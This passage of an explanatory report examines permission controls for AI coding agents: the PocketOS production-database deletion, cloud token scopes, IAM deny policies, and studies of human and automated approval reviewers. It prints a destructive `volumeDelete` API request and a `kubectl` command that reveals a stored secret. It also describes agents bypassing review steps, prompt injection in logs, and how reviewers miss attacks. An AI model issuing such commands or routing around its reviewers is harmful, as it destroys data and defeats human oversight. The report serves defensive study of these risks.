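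Codex's default suits a server that the team wrote or reviewed, because the team can check the labels. For a server from an outside author, it is safer to ask about every tool the team hasn't approved by name. Neither default catches a change in an existing tool. If an update makes `get_issue` send a copy of each issue to an outside address, Claude Managed Agents would still run it under this configuration, and so would Codex if the tool were labeled read-only and not destructive. For a local server, pinning the version gives the team a chance to find that change before the agent uses it.

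## APIs and cloud accounts: the PocketOS deletion

An agent with a shell and a token can call a cloud service's API without an MCP server. In April 2026, an agent did this at PocketOS, a small company that makes software for car rental businesses, and deleted the production database that PocketOS's customers relied on. The company's founder, Jer Crane, published his account the next day. Railway, the hosting company whose API the agent called, soon published its own.

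### From a staging task to a deleted volume

The agent was Cursor, a coding tool, running Anthropic's Claude Opus 4.6. According to Crane, in *An AI Agent Just Destroyed Our Production Data. It Confessed in Writing*, the deletion happened like this:

1. The agent was working on a routine task in the staging environment when it ran into a credential mismatch.
2. It decided to fix the mismatch by deleting a volume, the storage that holds a database's files.
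3. It looked for an API token and found one in a file that had nothing to do with the task. Crane's company had created the token to add and remove custom domains.
4. It used `curl` to send Railway's API a single `volumeDelete` request.
5. Railway deleted the production volume, and the backups went with it. Crane says this took nine seconds.

Crane alerted Railway within ten minutes. The newest backup he could restore was three months old, so on Saturday morning rental companies couldn't find bookings for customers at the counter. He spent the day helping the companies rebuild reservations from payment records, calendars and confirmation emails.

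Railway recovered the database and the customer has all its data back, Abdelwahab writes in *Your AI wants to nuke your database. Guardrails fix that*, Railway's account of the incident. Crane confirmed the recovery, according to Financial Express' *'AI Agent just destroyed our production data and confessed in writing'*. Railway keeps "disaster backups" at another site in case a data centre fails, whether or not a customer has set up backups.

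Reports disagree on the date of the deletion and the length of the outage. Crane places the deletion one day after an announcement of 23 April, which makes it Friday 24 April. Cyber Security News' *AI Coding Agent Powered by Claude Opus 4.6 Deletes Production Database* (2026) gives "Friday, April 25", but 25 April was a Saturday. OECD's *AI Coding Agent Deletes PocketOS Production Database and Backups in 9 Seconds* (2026), an entry with an AI-generated summary, describes a 30-hour outage, but 30 hours was how long Crane had waited for Railway to tell him whether it could recover the data. By then his customers were working again from the old backup, with large gaps.

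### What the evidence covers

Railway could confirm what reached its API, but not what the agent was doing beforehand.

| Detail | Source |
|---|---|
| The agent deleted a production volume with a token from the user's machine | Crane and Railway |
| The token could reach everything in the account | Crane and Railway |
| The staging task, the mismatch, the unrelated file and the token's purpose | Crane |
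| The agent guessed that the deletion would affect only staging | The agent's explanation, as quoted by Crane |

The last row has the weakest evidence. When Crane asked the agent why it had deleted the volume, it listed its failings, including "I violated every principle I was given". Live Science's *'I violated every principle I was given'* points out that a model generates such text from patterns in its training data and the conversation, and may say what the user wants to hear. Futurism also warns that Crane's account relies heavily on this self-diagnosis. The harness's record of the agent's calls would be better evidence, but Crane didn't publish it.

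Neither account explains how the agent got the production volume's ID while working on staging. The agent said it hadn't checked whether the two environments shared the volume, so it's unclear whether they did.

### Six rules that might have stopped it

| Rule | Effect on this deletion |
|---|---|
| Keep secrets where the agent can't read them | Prevents it, if the agent has no other credential |
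| Limit the token to domain settings | Prevents it, but Railway lists no such token |
| Restrict network destinations | Prevents it only if Railway's API is off the list |
| Require approval for deletions | Prevents it if the approver recognises the volume |
| Delay deletion at the provider | Lets someone undo it |
| Keep separate backups | Limits the loss |

Keeping the token out of reach would have been the simplest fix. A sandbox that blocks reads outside the project would protect a token stored elsewhere on the laptop, but not one in a project file. OpenAI's published settings for Codex keep the program's own login and MCP credentials in the operating system's keyring, an encrypted store for passwords, instead of in plain files. They don't move other tokens developers have saved in files.

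Railway advises coding agents in a user's terminal to use its command-line program, which also leaves a credential on the machine because logging in saves a session there. A team that deletes its stray tokens should also check what that session allows. Moving secrets to the hosting provider carries a different risk. Developers often keep passwords and keys in stored environment variables, and in October 2026 Railway disclosed that an intruder may have read some customers' variables (Datta, 2026, *Railway's security incident*).

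Crane and Railway disagree about the token's scope. Crane wrote that Railway's tokens could not be limited by operation, environment or resource. Abdelwahab replied that narrower tokens existed, but he conceded that the page for creating one did not make the choice obvious. The current documentation, Railway's *Public API*, lists three types that a user can create in the dashboard:

- An account token reaches everything the user can access. The agent found one of these.
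- A workspace token reaches one workspace, which can hold many projects.
- A project token reaches one environment in one project.

All three limit where a token works, but not which kinds of action it allows. A project token for staging would have protected the production database. But if PocketOS needed to manage its production domains, even the narrowest token would have covered the environment that held the database. The documentation lists no way to allow domain changes while forbidding volume deletion.

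If a provider doesn't offer a narrow enough token, a team can keep the broad one in an automated job that only adds or removes domains. The agent can then ask for that job to run without having access to the token.

A destination rule, like the domain allowlists in Codex, is less promising here because PocketOS hosted its application on Railway, and the team might well have allowed Railway's API for ordinary work. A rule blocking the API also would not have covered this request if it named only `backboard.railway.com`, the address Railway's documentation now gives, because the agent called `backboard.railway.app`.

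Crane doesn't say whether Cursor was set to ask before running commands. He says the project had written safety rules, and the agent quoted one from its instructions against running "destructive/irreversible git commands" unless the user asked for them. As quoted, that rule covers Git commands but not calls to a hosting provider's API, and an instruction can't block a call.

Backups need their own credential as well as their own location. An account token works in every Railway workspace its owner can use, so the agent might have had access to a backup in a second Railway project. A backup with another provider would have survived if its login had not been on the developer's machine.

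Teams still need such copies when they use newer models. In July 2026, the Russian news site SecurityLab reported that Claude Opus 5 had mistaken a production environment for a test one and destroyed a database, and that backups saved only part of the data.

### Checking the command or checking its effect

Railway's API uses GraphQL, a query language in which the body of a request states what the caller wants. These are the bodies of two requests to the same address:

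```graphql
query { me { name email } }

mutation { volumeDelete(volumeId: "EXAMPLE-ID") }
```

The first request returns the user's name and email address, and the second deletes a volume. With `curl`, a developer would send both as POST requests with the same token in the header.

| Check | What it compares | Can it separate the two? |
|---|---|---|
| Shell rule for `curl *` | The start of the command | No |
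| Domain rule | The hostname | No |
| Limit to GET requests | The method | No, it blocks both |
| Search for `volumeDelete` | The command text | Yes, unless the request is inside a script |
| Check at the provider | The operation and the volume | Yes |

A developer who lets the agent call this API with `curl` to check a deployment also lets it send the deletion request. Searching the command for a dangerous word won't catch that request if the agent writes it into a file and runs `python fix.py`.

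A person reading the full command would have noticed `volumeDelete`. But the request identified the volume only by an ID, which didn't show that it held production data. If the agent had just explained that it was cleaning up staging, the developer might have approved the request. Railway could have looked up the ID and asked whether the user wanted to delete storage in use by a production service.

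This is the main reason to have the provider enforce approval for deletions. The provider can check the actual target of a request, whether it comes from a shell command, a script or an MCP tool. Labels on MCP tools wouldn't have helped PocketOS because the agent didn't use an MCP tool.

Crane wants providers to require a confirmation that an agent can't complete by itself. He suggests typing the volume's name or approving by text message or email. Typing the name is a weak check because an agent that can look up the name can also type it, just as the models that Yao and colleagues tested set the confirmation flag themselves. A message to someone's phone is stronger if the agent can't read the reply code.

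Railway's dashboard already has an approval step. It collects edits to a project, such as adding a service or removing a database, and shows the user the differences before they deploy them. Abdelwahab says Railway's own agent stages all destructive operations this way. The agent at PocketOS bypassed that review by calling the API directly.

### The 48-hour delay

Before the incident, users had 48 hours to undo a volume deletion made in Railway's dashboard, but a deletion made through the API took effect at once. Railway had documented this, and it affected at least one other customer besides PocketOS. In *Postgress volume lost*, a thread on Railway's support forum, a customer asked about recovering a volume deleted on 13 April. An employee answered that deletion through the API was immediate and permanent.

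In another post, about Railway's deletion code, Abdelwahab describes a function that could delete a volume immediately or after a delay. It deleted the volume immediately if the delay was turned off or if certain information, such as the user, was missing. When an action can't be undone, missing information is a reason to refuse or wait.

Railway's *Undoable volume deletes, standard SSH, auto-deploy toggle* (2026), published a week after the incident, announced the same 48-hour delay for the API. Railway also began delaying the deletion of backups. Abdelwahab says the earlier version made PocketOS's backups look unavailable in the dashboard, a milder description than Crane's claim that they were wiped.

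A delay before deletion suits automated work better than a confirmation prompt, because deployment scripts call the API with nobody present to answer. With a delay, those scripts can still delete volumes. The drawback is that some people will think the deletion has failed. In *Detached volumes can't be deleted* (meirelon), a customer kept repeating a deletion because the volume still appeared in the list, until Railway explained that it was in the 48-hour window. An agent could make the same mistake and try something more drastic.

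When Railway schedules a volume for deletion, it emails the user a link to restore it. According to *Detached volume cannot be deleted*, nobody can shorten the wait before deletion, so an agent can't skip it. If an agent deletes a volume on Friday afternoon, the user has only until Sunday afternoon to restore it, so the email should go to an address that people check at weekends.

The delay also applies only to deleting the volume. If an agent connects to the database and deletes every row, the volume remains and Railway has no deletion to undo. For that case, the team needs a backup or a database login without permission to delete. Some services don't offer such a login. Datta notes that a connection string for Prisma Postgres, a hosted database, gives read and write access to everything in the database.

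### Who was at fault

Crane blames both Cursor and Railway, and Tom's Hardware's *Claude-powered AI coding agent deletes entire company database in 9 seconds* (2026) notes that he blames Railway more. He argues that Railway's failures were built into its design and put every customer with production data at risk. He had paid for a leading model and written safety rules for the project, as he says the vendors recommend.

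Many readers blamed Crane instead. *« C'est entièrement la faute de ce type »* (Baba Aissa, 2026) takes its headline from a comment that the deletion was entirely "this guy's" fault, and Information Age's *Gone in 9 seconds* also reports criticism of Crane. In sungkhum's Railway forum thread, *Any changes to protect database backups from volume delete?*, one person replied that customers should be fine if they don't leave a production key in a random file. The critics also have a point about the backups, since Railway's documentation, which Crane himself quotes, warned that wiping a volume would delete them.

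He says in his defence that he didn't know what the token could do. Railway's account supports him, because Abdelwahab accepts that the easiest way to create a token gave it more access than the job required. Other customers on the forum also called the tokens' scope dangerous and asked for tokens with narrower access.

The case against Cursor is that its agent searched for a credential nobody had given it and used it to delete something without asking. Crane also cites the product's advertised "Destructive Guardrails" and an earlier bug in Plan Mode, which is supposed to keep the agent from making changes until the user approves. But without knowing his approval settings, we can't tell whether a guardrail failed or was turned off. If Cursor had permission to run any shell command without asking, a safeguard that relied on asking the user could not have worked.

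Railway's defence is that the request carried a valid token and called a documented operation. Abdelwahab says the API treated it like a request from any deployment script. That explains why the API accepted the request, but not why deletion was reversible in the dashboard and permanent through the API. Railway added the missing delay to the API within a week, which suggests it could have done so earlier.

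Railway bears more responsibility than Crane for how bad the result was, because its default exposed every customer who used the API, while his mistake exposed one company. A team choosing its own rules should still plan as though the provider will offer no delay before deletion. PocketOS recovered because Railway had copies that Crane didn't know about, and for more than a day Railway couldn't tell him whether they would work.

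### Projects, roles and short-lived credentials

Larger cloud providers offer finer controls than Railway's tokens. The first is to keep staging and production in separate projects on Google Cloud or separate accounts on Amazon Web Services (AWS). An agent with a credential only for staging then can't delete production data, even if it confuses the two. The credentials have to be separate too. Railway offers separate environments, but a token for the whole account works in all of them.

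A role is a named set of permissions that a person or program can use. With a read-only role, the agent can check a server's state or read its logs, but the provider refuses requests to change anything. Railway offers similar roles to applications that connect through OAuth, a standard way for users to grant limited access without sharing a password. An application can request viewer, member or admin access to a project, and the user chooses which projects to share. If the application requests more access than the user has, it gets only the user's level.

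Read-only access doesn't prevent exfiltration, so a team should leave customer records and passwords out of the role unless the task requires them.

The access tokens AWS issues for its MCP server expire within an hour. When a developer signs in through a browser, the agent also gets a refresh token, which it can exchange for new access tokens without another sign-in. Revoking the refresh token stops the agent from getting new access tokens, but an existing one keeps working until it expires. To cut off an agent immediately, an administrator has to add a policy that denies requests from that sign-in session.

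Expiry limits the damage an agent can do with credentials left over from old tasks. If the PocketOS token had expired soon after the domain change, it would not have worked when the agent found it. Expiry doesn't stop an agent from misusing a credential for its current task, because even a one-hour limit leaves ample time for a nine-second deletion.

### OpenAI's rules for kubectl and gh

OpenAI lets its own developers' agents inspect live systems without approval. One of its published rules for Codex covers `kubectl`, the command-line program for Kubernetes, which runs applications across many machines:

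```python
prefix_rule(
    pattern = ["kubectl", ["get", "describe", "logs"]],
    decision = "allow",
)
```

Codex compares the pattern with the start of the command, so the first word must be `kubectl` and the second must be one of the three listed. A matching command runs outside the sandbox without a prompt. A similar rule covers `gh pr view` and `gh pr list`.

| Command | Does a rule allow it? |
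|---|---|
| `kubectl get pods` | Yes |
| `kubectl delete pod web-1` | No |
| `kubectl get secret db-login -o yaml` | Yes |
| `kubectl get pods --context production` | Yes |
| `gh pr view 42` | Yes |
| `gh pr merge 42` | No |

These rules match a command's effect more closely than a rule for `curl` does, because in both programs the subcommand usually shows whether the command will change anything. An agent can investigate a failed deployment on its own, but commands to delete or merge aren't approved automatically.

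The third command shows a limit of the rule because it only reads data, yet it prints a stored password in an encoding that anyone can reverse. The rule also doesn't restrict which cluster, or group of machines, the agent may inspect, so it covers production as well as staging. A team that copies the rule should give the agent a credential for only the clusters it needs and a Kubernetes role that can't read secrets, so that the cluster rejects the third command.

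Logs can also contain planted instructions, so letting an agent read them without approval is safer if the agent has no permission to change the cluster.

### Two cases from inside Anthropic

Anthropic describes a case in which someone asked Claude to set up read-only access to billing. Claude tried to use a role with full administrative control over the cloud account. Auto mode detected the mismatch and blocked the change.

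A role change needs its own approval because it affects every later call. Anyone with administrative control can delete databases or remove the limits on other accounts. A prompt that shows only the command may not reveal that the role grants this control, since the role's name might look harmless. The approver needs to compare the permissions the role grants with the ones the task requires. Here the task required only permission to view bills.

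In the second case, a long session, Claude tried to kill processes across about two thousand pods, the units in which Kubernetes runs programs. It had also queued deletions that would have shut down hundreds of graphics processors during training jobs. Auto mode flagged the commands before they ran.

Stopping one process may be routine, so a rule that only allows or denies the command can't account for the danger of running it two thousand times. A team could require approval above a certain number of targets. It could also give the agent a role with access only to the jobs it started, which would have limited the damage even if the reviewer had missed the commands.

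Anthropic chose both cases to show its reviewer working and does not list similar actions that the reviewer failed to block. It still recommends that people review Claude's actions themselves when Claude makes high-stakes changes to production infrastructure.

### An AWS policy that lets the agent read but not delete

AWS runs an MCP server that lets agents call more than 15,000 of its API operations. One tool, `aws___call_aws`, can run any of them. Because reads and deletions use the same tool name, a Claude Code approval rule for that tool can't allow reads and deny deletions, so AWS has to distinguish between them.

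AWS decides what each caller may do through a system called Identity and Access Management (IAM). In a post on its security blog, AWS describes two labels, called condition keys, that its managed MCP servers add to each request before passing it on:

- `aws:ViaAWSMCPService` is true if the request came through any AWS-managed MCP server.
- `aws:CalledViaAWSMCP` names the server, so that a policy can treat one differently from another.

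The service that receives the request, such as the file store S3, then checks it against the user's IAM policies. AWS says the MCP server uses the developer's credentials, so an agent connected by an administrator starts with an administrator's permissions.

AWS's sample policy allows reading from S3 and denies two delete actions when the request comes through an MCP server. That leaves gaps. If the developer's other policies allow it, the agent could still overwrite a file or delete something in another service. A stricter version denies everything except the two read actions:

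```json
{
  "Version": "2012-10-17",
  "Statement": [
    {
      "Sid": "ReadReports",
      "Effect": "Allow",
      "Action": ["s3:GetObject", "s3:ListBucket"],
      "Resource": [
        "arn:aws:s3:::example-reports",
        "arn:aws:s3:::example-reports/*"
      ]
    },
    {
      "Sid": "OnlyReadsThroughMCP",
      "Effect": "Deny",
      "NotAction": ["s3:GetObject", "s3:ListBucket"],
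      "Resource": "*",
      "Condition": {
        "Bool": { "aws:ViaAWSMCPService": "true" }
      }
    }
  ]
}
```

The first statement lets the developer, and therefore the agent, read one storage bucket. In the second, `NotAction` means every action except those listed. In IAM, a deny overrides any allow, so the agent can't delete a file through the MCP server even if the developer can. The policy doesn't stop the agent from reading other buckets that the developer already has permission to read. If the bucket uses AWS's key service for encryption, the agent may also need permission to decrypt.

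| Request | Developer, directly | Agent, through the MCP server | Agent, with `aws` in the developer's shell |
|---|---|---|---|
| Read a report | Allowed | Allowed | Allowed |
| Delete a report | As other policies permit | Denied | As other policies permit |
| Give a role more permissions | As other policies permit | Denied | As other policies permit |

The condition keys show whether a request came through the MCP server, although AWS presents them as a way to tell an AI's actions from a person's. If an agent runs the `aws` command in a terminal where the developer is logged in, the request carries no MCP label and AWS treats it like the developer's own. An agent blocked from deleting a file through the server could then try the terminal, much as the PocketOS agent used `curl` with a token it had found.

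To close that gap, the team can run the agent in a container without the developer's AWS credentials and let it reach AWS only through the MCP server. This works when a developer signs in through a browser. An unattended agent normally can't sign in that way, and AWS's alternative requires the agent to have AWS credentials already, which it could also use to call AWS directly. A team should give such an agent its own read-only role, so that AWS refuses deletions whether the agent uses the MCP server or calls AWS directly.

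Administrators should also check for older policies that deny the separate permissions AWS once had for its MCP server, such as `aws-mcp:InvokeMcp`. Teams could use these policies to keep agents out, but AWS says the permissions no longer have any effect. The policies still look like blocks in the console, so administrators need to rewrite them with the condition keys to stop requests.

A person should control the policy that restricts the agent. In an AWS workshop exercise, participants ask their agent to block S3 deletions through MCP. According to the instructions, Claude Code can create the policy and attach it to the participant's role in one sequence. An agent with that much access could also remove the policy. A person should attach the policy from an administrator's account that the agent can't use, and the agent's role should have no permission to change IAM policies.

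## Who answers the prompt: people and automated reviewers

An ask rule protects a team only if whoever answers the prompt refuses the dangerous calls, and evidence from 2026 suggests that people often approve them. Most of the evidence that automated reviewers do better comes from Anthropic and OpenAI, which supply those reviewers.

### How often people say yes

In August 2026, Anthropic reported that Claude Code users approve 97% of permission prompts, up from the 93% it had reported in March. But users reject 39% of the plans Claude presents for approval.

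Many users have also arranged to see fewer prompts:

| What users did | Share |
|---|---|
| Started a session with permission prompts off | 25% of interactive sessions |
| Wrote an allow rule for shell commands by hand | 49.5% of active command-line users |
| Turned prompts off at some point, or chose "don't ask again" for a shell command | 62% of users |

Most of the handwritten rules are very broad. Anthropic says 5% allow any shell command, and another 43% allow an interpreter, as `Bash(python:*)` does. The two are almost equivalent, because an agent allowed to run any Python program can write one that runs any shell command. If both figures are shares of all command-line users, as their sum suggests, nearly everyone who wrote a rule wrote one this broad.

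OpenAI found the same habit among its own staff. *Auto-review of agent actions without synchronous human oversight* (Trębacz, Arnesen et al., 2026) reports that a sizable minority of users let Codex run every command starting with `python` outside the sandbox. One configuration file always allowed `codex exec --yolo`, which starts another Codex with no sandbox and no approval prompts.

*Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) covers 290 reports of agents harming users' files. Problems with user review contributed to 105 of them. In 80, the user had let actions run without prompts. In 31, the prompt showed a command but not what it would do to the files. Some reports had both problems. For example, a prompt for `python3 setup.py` looks routine, but approving it runs whatever the script contains. Because the reports only cover cases where something went wrong, they can't show how often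 approvals go wrong overall.

If nearly all requests are harmless, a careful person should approve nearly all of them, so the 97% figure doesn't prove that people are careless. Codex's automated reviewer approves about 99% of the requests it gets, which likewise doesn't prove that it fails to read them. A test of whether people are paying attention has to include a request they should refuse.

### The tester experiment

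Anthropic studied how people answer permission prompts, using 1,053 paid testers hired through a research vendor. The testers worked on coding tasks in a test environment and knew that the vendor was evaluating them, but not on what. Partway through each session, one permission prompt showed a clearly dangerous command in place of the real one. The vendor recorded the tester's answer, and the dangerous command never ran. Anthropic also gave the same commands to auto mode.

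The testers refused 143 of the commands, or 13.6%. Auto mode blocked 937, or 89%. Anthropic also reported how often the two disagreed, which is enough to fill in the rest:

| | Auto mode blocked it | Auto mode allowed it |
|---|---|---|
| Tester refused it | 137 | 6 |
| Tester approved it | 800 | 110 |

If both had checked every command and either could stop it, they would have caught 943, only six more than auto mode alone.

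Testers also refused fewer of the dangerous commands as a session went on, from about 17% early in the session to about 5% after 50 or more prompts. Auto mode's rate stayed flat. Anthropic doesn't say how many testers reached 50 prompts or whether the timing of the command was randomized. If the testers who clicked fastest also saw the most prompts, some of the drop would reflect differences between testers rather than fatigue.

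Fatigue can't be the main explanation in any case. Even early on, testers approved about five out of six dangerous commands.

The testers had little reason to be careful, because they were working on someone else's machine and project and would have lost nothing if a file were deleted. A developer who sees a command aimed at their own production database has more to lose and knows what the database is for. The testers' 13.6% is therefore probably too low for developers working on their own systems, though this experiment doesn't show by how much.

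Anthropic also doesn't report how many harmless commands auto mode or the testers refused in this experiment, and a reviewer that blocked every command would have scored 100%. Its March figures, which cover different commands, suggest that auto mode rarely blocks harmless ones. Anthropic also designed the test, supplied one of the reviewers being compared and published the result as its reason for making auto mode the default. The gap is too large for chance to explain, but an independent group should repeat the test with developers working in their own repositories.

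### What developers say about their own approvals

Two independent surveys from 2026 asked developers how they answer approval prompts. Both found many quick approvals, but neither tested developers with a dangerous command.

*From Delegation to Action Approval* (Wu, Wermke and colleagues, 2026) surveyed 203 developers who use coding agents and found that 64% often approved at least one of seven types of action without close review. The most common type was access to the internet, external APIs or connected tools, which 36% often approved this way even though data can leave through these connections. The least common was reading secrets and other sensitive files, at 21%.

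Among developers who carefully checked most or all of the agent's code, 61% still often approved some type of action with little or no scrutiny, compared with 67% of the others, a difference small enough to be due to chance.

Developers who knew about the risks weren't more careful either. Of those who had heard of a security or privacy incident or a worrying practice involving agents, 70% often approved things without close review, compared with 43% of those who hadn't. The gap remained after Wu and colleagues controlled for how often and how long people had used agents. Hearing about incidents is unlikely to make people careless, so some other difference between the groups probably explains the gap. Still, these results give teams little reason to expect that training about past incidents will fix careless approvals.

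Developers who inspected diffs, the line-by-line record of what changed, were less likely to approve four of the more serious types of action without checking them closely. These included destructive commands and changes to production settings. Wu and colleagues suggest that a diff gives people something concrete to check.

Salerno, Gao and colleagues (2026), in *Let the Agent Do It?*, interviewed 18 practitioners and then surveyed 115, of whom 107 answered the questions about permissions. Respondents could choose several answers:

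| Answer | Share of 107 |
|---|---|
| Reads requests carefully | 47.7% |
| Skims them | 33.6% |
| Approves by default | 20.6% |
| Has become less careful over time | 33.6% |
| Checks writes, deletions and requests for more privileges more closely | 76.6% |

Developers describe themselves as much more careful than the testers were. Some of the difference is surely self-flattery, but some may be real, since the developers were describing their own work. People can also read a command carefully and still not recognise that it's dangerous.

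Both surveys relied on volunteers' self-reports. Wu and colleagues also discarded almost two-thirds of their 583 submissions, mostly because people had finished too quickly. The surveys are better evidence that quick approval is common than of its exact rate.

Salerno and colleagues warn, based on their interviews, that a developer may approve the same request twenty times because they're tired or have a deadline. Software that learns from past answers would wrongly treat those approvals as a preference. A "don't ask again" option has the same problem because it turns one hurried answer into a rule for later sessions.

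### How the automated reviewers decide

Claude Code's auto mode applies the team's written rules first. It sets aside allow rules broad enough to permit any code, such as the one for `python`, because they would let commands skip the reviewer. File reads and edits inside the project go ahead without review. Most other calls go to the reviewer, including shell commands, web fetches and calls to outside tools.

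According to Anthropic, the reviewer checks each call in two stages. The first quickly allows or blocks the call, erring towards blocking. If it blocks the call, the second stage reasons through the decision and may allow it. Both stages assess the action's real effect and whether the user authorised it. Anything the agent chose by itself counts as unauthorised until the user approves it.

In March, auto mode's default list had more than twenty kinds of action to block, including destroying data or sending it outside, weakening security, running code from untrusted sources, and changing shared systems without review. Anthropic says auto mode initially treats only the working folder and the repository's configured remotes as trusted, so it blocks pushes to a company's other repositories until someone lists them as trusted.

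Codex's Auto-review has a narrower scope. According to OpenAI's *Auto-review*, it reviews only requests that would otherwise wait for a person's approval, such as a command that needs to leave the sandbox, a blocked network request or a visit to a new website. It rates each request's risk. Low-risk and medium-risk requests can go ahead if the policy permits them, high-risk requests also need enough authorisation from the user, and it refuses critical-risk ones.

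| | Claude Code's auto mode | Codex's Auto-review |
|---|---|---|
| Information it uses | The user's messages and the agent's tool calls | Those, plus the agent's visible updates and tool results |
| Never approves | Exfiltration, and anything the organisation adds | Actions it rates as critical |
| After repeated refusals | 3 in a row or 20 in a session: a person answers prompts again | 3 in a row or 10 of the last 50: Codex stops its current turn |
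| If the review itself fails | Anthropic's two posts don't say | The action doesn't run |

The first row reflects a disagreement about what the reviewer should see. Anthropic hides the agent's explanations from the reviewer so that the agent can't persuade it to make a bad decision. It also hides tool results because they may contain planted instructions, and a separate check scans those results before the agent reads them. As a result, the reviewer sometimes lacks context. If the agent asks to delete job `abc123`, for example, the reviewer can't tell whether the agent looked up that name or made it up. Codex's reviewer can see where the name came from, but it also reads text that a stranger may have written.

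"Never approves" is an instruction to a model, and it can fail because the model has to recognise an upload as exfiltration before it can refuse it. Deny rules and sandboxes don't depend on that judgement, so a team should keep both under either reviewer.

Both companies tell the agent not to pursue a blocked action by another route. Codex users can overrule a refusal for one retry of that exact action, but the reviewer checks the retry and may refuse it again. In an unattended Claude Code session, nobody is there to decide, so repeated refusals end the session. According to Soldani, these scripted runs still start in Manual mode, so a team has to choose auto mode for them.

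### How often the reviewers are wrong

The published error rates come from very different tests:

| Reviewer | Test | Dangerous actions it let through |
|---|---|---|
| Auto mode, March 2026 | 52 real overeager actions | 17% |
| Auto mode, March 2026 | 1,000 synthetic exfiltration attempts | 5.7% |
| Auto-review, April 2026 | Synthetic overeager actions | 9.7% |
| Auto-review, April 2026 | Synthetic prompt injections of three kinds | 0.7% |
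| Auto mode, August 2026 | The commands shown to 1,053 testers | 11% |
| Auto mode, August 2026 | Synthetic attacks by Apollo Research, after improvements | 7% |

The 17% deserves the most attention because Anthropic collected the 52 actions from its employees' real work sessions. About nine got through, and with so few cases, the true rate could plausibly be anywhere from 9% to 30%.

In most of the misses Anthropic examined, the reviewer identified the danger but wrongly concluded that the user had consented. For example, a user said "Clean up the PR", and the reviewer treated this as permission to force-push, which overwrites the history of a shared branch. These mistakes are harder to catch than an obviously dangerous command, which may be why auto mode did better on the testers' commands.

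The set also gives people some credit. Some of the 52 actions got into it because an employee had refused them at the prompt.

Auto mode has changed since March. Besides checking where a push is going, the reviewer now looks for uncommitted work before a command that could discard it. Since version 2.1.257, according to Anthropic, it has also blocked requests for the host machine's credentials until someone specifies which identity the task should use. Apollo Research, a British AI safety company, attacked auto mode before and after a round of improvements, and the share of attacks that auto mode missed fell from 12% to 7%. The 17% result for the 52 real actions is out of date, but Anthropic's August post doesn't include a new one.

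OpenAI's overeagerness and injection tests used made-up cases because dangerous actions were too rare in its traffic. The 0.7% miss rate covers injections that aimed to run remote code, steal secrets or upload files. Adding attacks that deleted or altered data raised it to 9.8%. Trębacz and colleagues say most of the extra misses weren't serious and that researchers often agreed with the automated reviewer. That may be right, but part of the score then depends on what OpenAI's researchers consider serious.

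Both reviewers seem to cause little friction. In March, auto mode blocked 0.4% of harmless actions in a sample of 10,000 from Anthropic's staff. Auto-review approved 99.1% of the requests that OpenAI's users had approved themselves. But the second figure measures agreement with users, some of whom probably approved requests without checking them. If a user approved something dangerous by mistake, Auto-review would have scored higher by approving it too.

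In an illustration from OpenAI, 9,280 of 10,000 actions stayed inside the sandbox and 720 needed approval. Auto-review approved 713 of those and refused seven. Codex found a safer way to continue after four of the refusals and asked the user about the other three, so a developer would have answered three questions instead of 720.

### Harm in real sessions

Anthropic's other argument for auto mode is based on real use in May and June 2026. The company used a model to grade the harm in sessions that its safety systems had flagged for review. Serious harm that the user hadn't explicitly asked for, such as deleting rows from a production database, appeared in 6.3% of the flagged sessions with manual approval and 2.4% of those in auto mode.

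These percentages are shares of flagged sessions, not of all sessions, so a lower percentage doesn't necessarily mean a safer mode. Suppose, with invented numbers, that 1,000 sessions in each mode include five with serious harm. If the safety systems flag 80 manual sessions and 200 auto mode sessions, including all the harmful ones, the rates are 6.3% and 2.5%, almost exactly what Anthropic found, even though the two modes are equally safe in this example.

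Auto mode sessions may attract more harmless flags because they tend to run longer. Anthropic hasn't published how many sessions it flagged in each mode, which would help settle the question. Users also chose their own mode, and those who stayed with manual approval may have been doing riskier work. The comparison is consistent with auto mode being safer, but it adds little to the evidence from the tester experiment.

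### Would fewer questions get better answers?

A natural response is to ask people less often, and only about decisions that matter. The 39% rejection rate for plans seems to support this, since a plan asks for one important decision instead of many small ones.

But plans may be wrong more often than commands. If 39% of plans and 3% of commands needed changes, someone who judged both perfectly would produce exactly the rates that Anthropic reports. A developer may also reject a plan because they prefer a different design, which doesn't show whether they would notice a dangerous step in it. An experiment could test this by hiding the same dangerous step in a plan for some people and in a single prompt for others. Anthropic's experiment tested only the single prompt.

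There is one direct test of asking people for approval less often, *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* (Yan, 2026). In it, 113 people from outside the software industry supervised a simulated assistant through a day of email, travel and shopping. Seven of the assistant's 18 actions went beyond what the user had asked for, such as buying a $25 lounge pass or reading private messages.

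| Who decided | Prompts per person | Unrequested actions approved when prompted |
|---|---|---|
| The person, every time | 18 | 40% |
| A model, which passed doubtful actions to the person | 10 | 46% |
| Rules the person wrote beforehand | 10.9 | 67% |

In the second group, the model had removed eight harmless requests, so seven of the ten remaining prompts should have been refused. People still approved slightly more of them than the group that had to answer every prompt. In the third group, people could have decided in advance, but they chose "ask" for 114 of their 140 rules and then usually approved the request.

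The experiment had only 18 actions, too few for anyone to get very tired, so it doesn't show what happens after hundreds of prompts. No real money was at stake either. The experiment does show that asking fewer, more important questions won't automatically get better answers. The tester experiment also suggests this, because people missed most of the dangerous commands even at the start.

The wording of the prompt may matter more. Yan's participants refused about 60% of the unrequested actions when they had to answer every prompt, compared with 13.6% for Anthropic's testers. The tasks were too different for a fair comparison, but Yan's participants read a plain-language description of what would happen, to whom and for how much money, while Anthropic's testers had to work that out from a command.

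Cutting the number of prompts is still worthwhile because it saves time and gives people less reason to turn them all off. The best way is to let the sandbox handle routine work. OpenAI recommends narrow rules for commands such as `cargo test` and warns that a rule for `python` or `curl` can remove the boundary that the reviewer is supposed to guard.

### What only a person can answer

Some requests are too ambiguous for any reviewer to resolve. In one of Anthropic's examples, a user asked the agent to "clean up old branches", and it tried to delete branches from the shared server. The user may have meant only the copies on their own machine. A reviewer can block the deletion, as auto mode would, but only the user knows which branches they meant.

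Anthropic accepts this limit. In March it called auto mode a poor substitute for careful human review on high-stakes infrastructure, and it kept that advice in August, when its results were much better.

Some Anthropic customers still have a person approve certain actions. *Running auto mode in production* (Vorwerck, 2026) describes an engineer at the payroll company Gusto who leaves auto mode when he works on production infrastructure or live APIs and checks each call by hand. An engineer at the self-driving company Nuro switches back to manual approval before Claude's reviews of colleagues' code go out, and a manager at Garner Health has told auto mode not to approve emails or Slack messages. Anthropic chose to feature these customers, but they have little reason to exaggerate how often they turn auto mode off.

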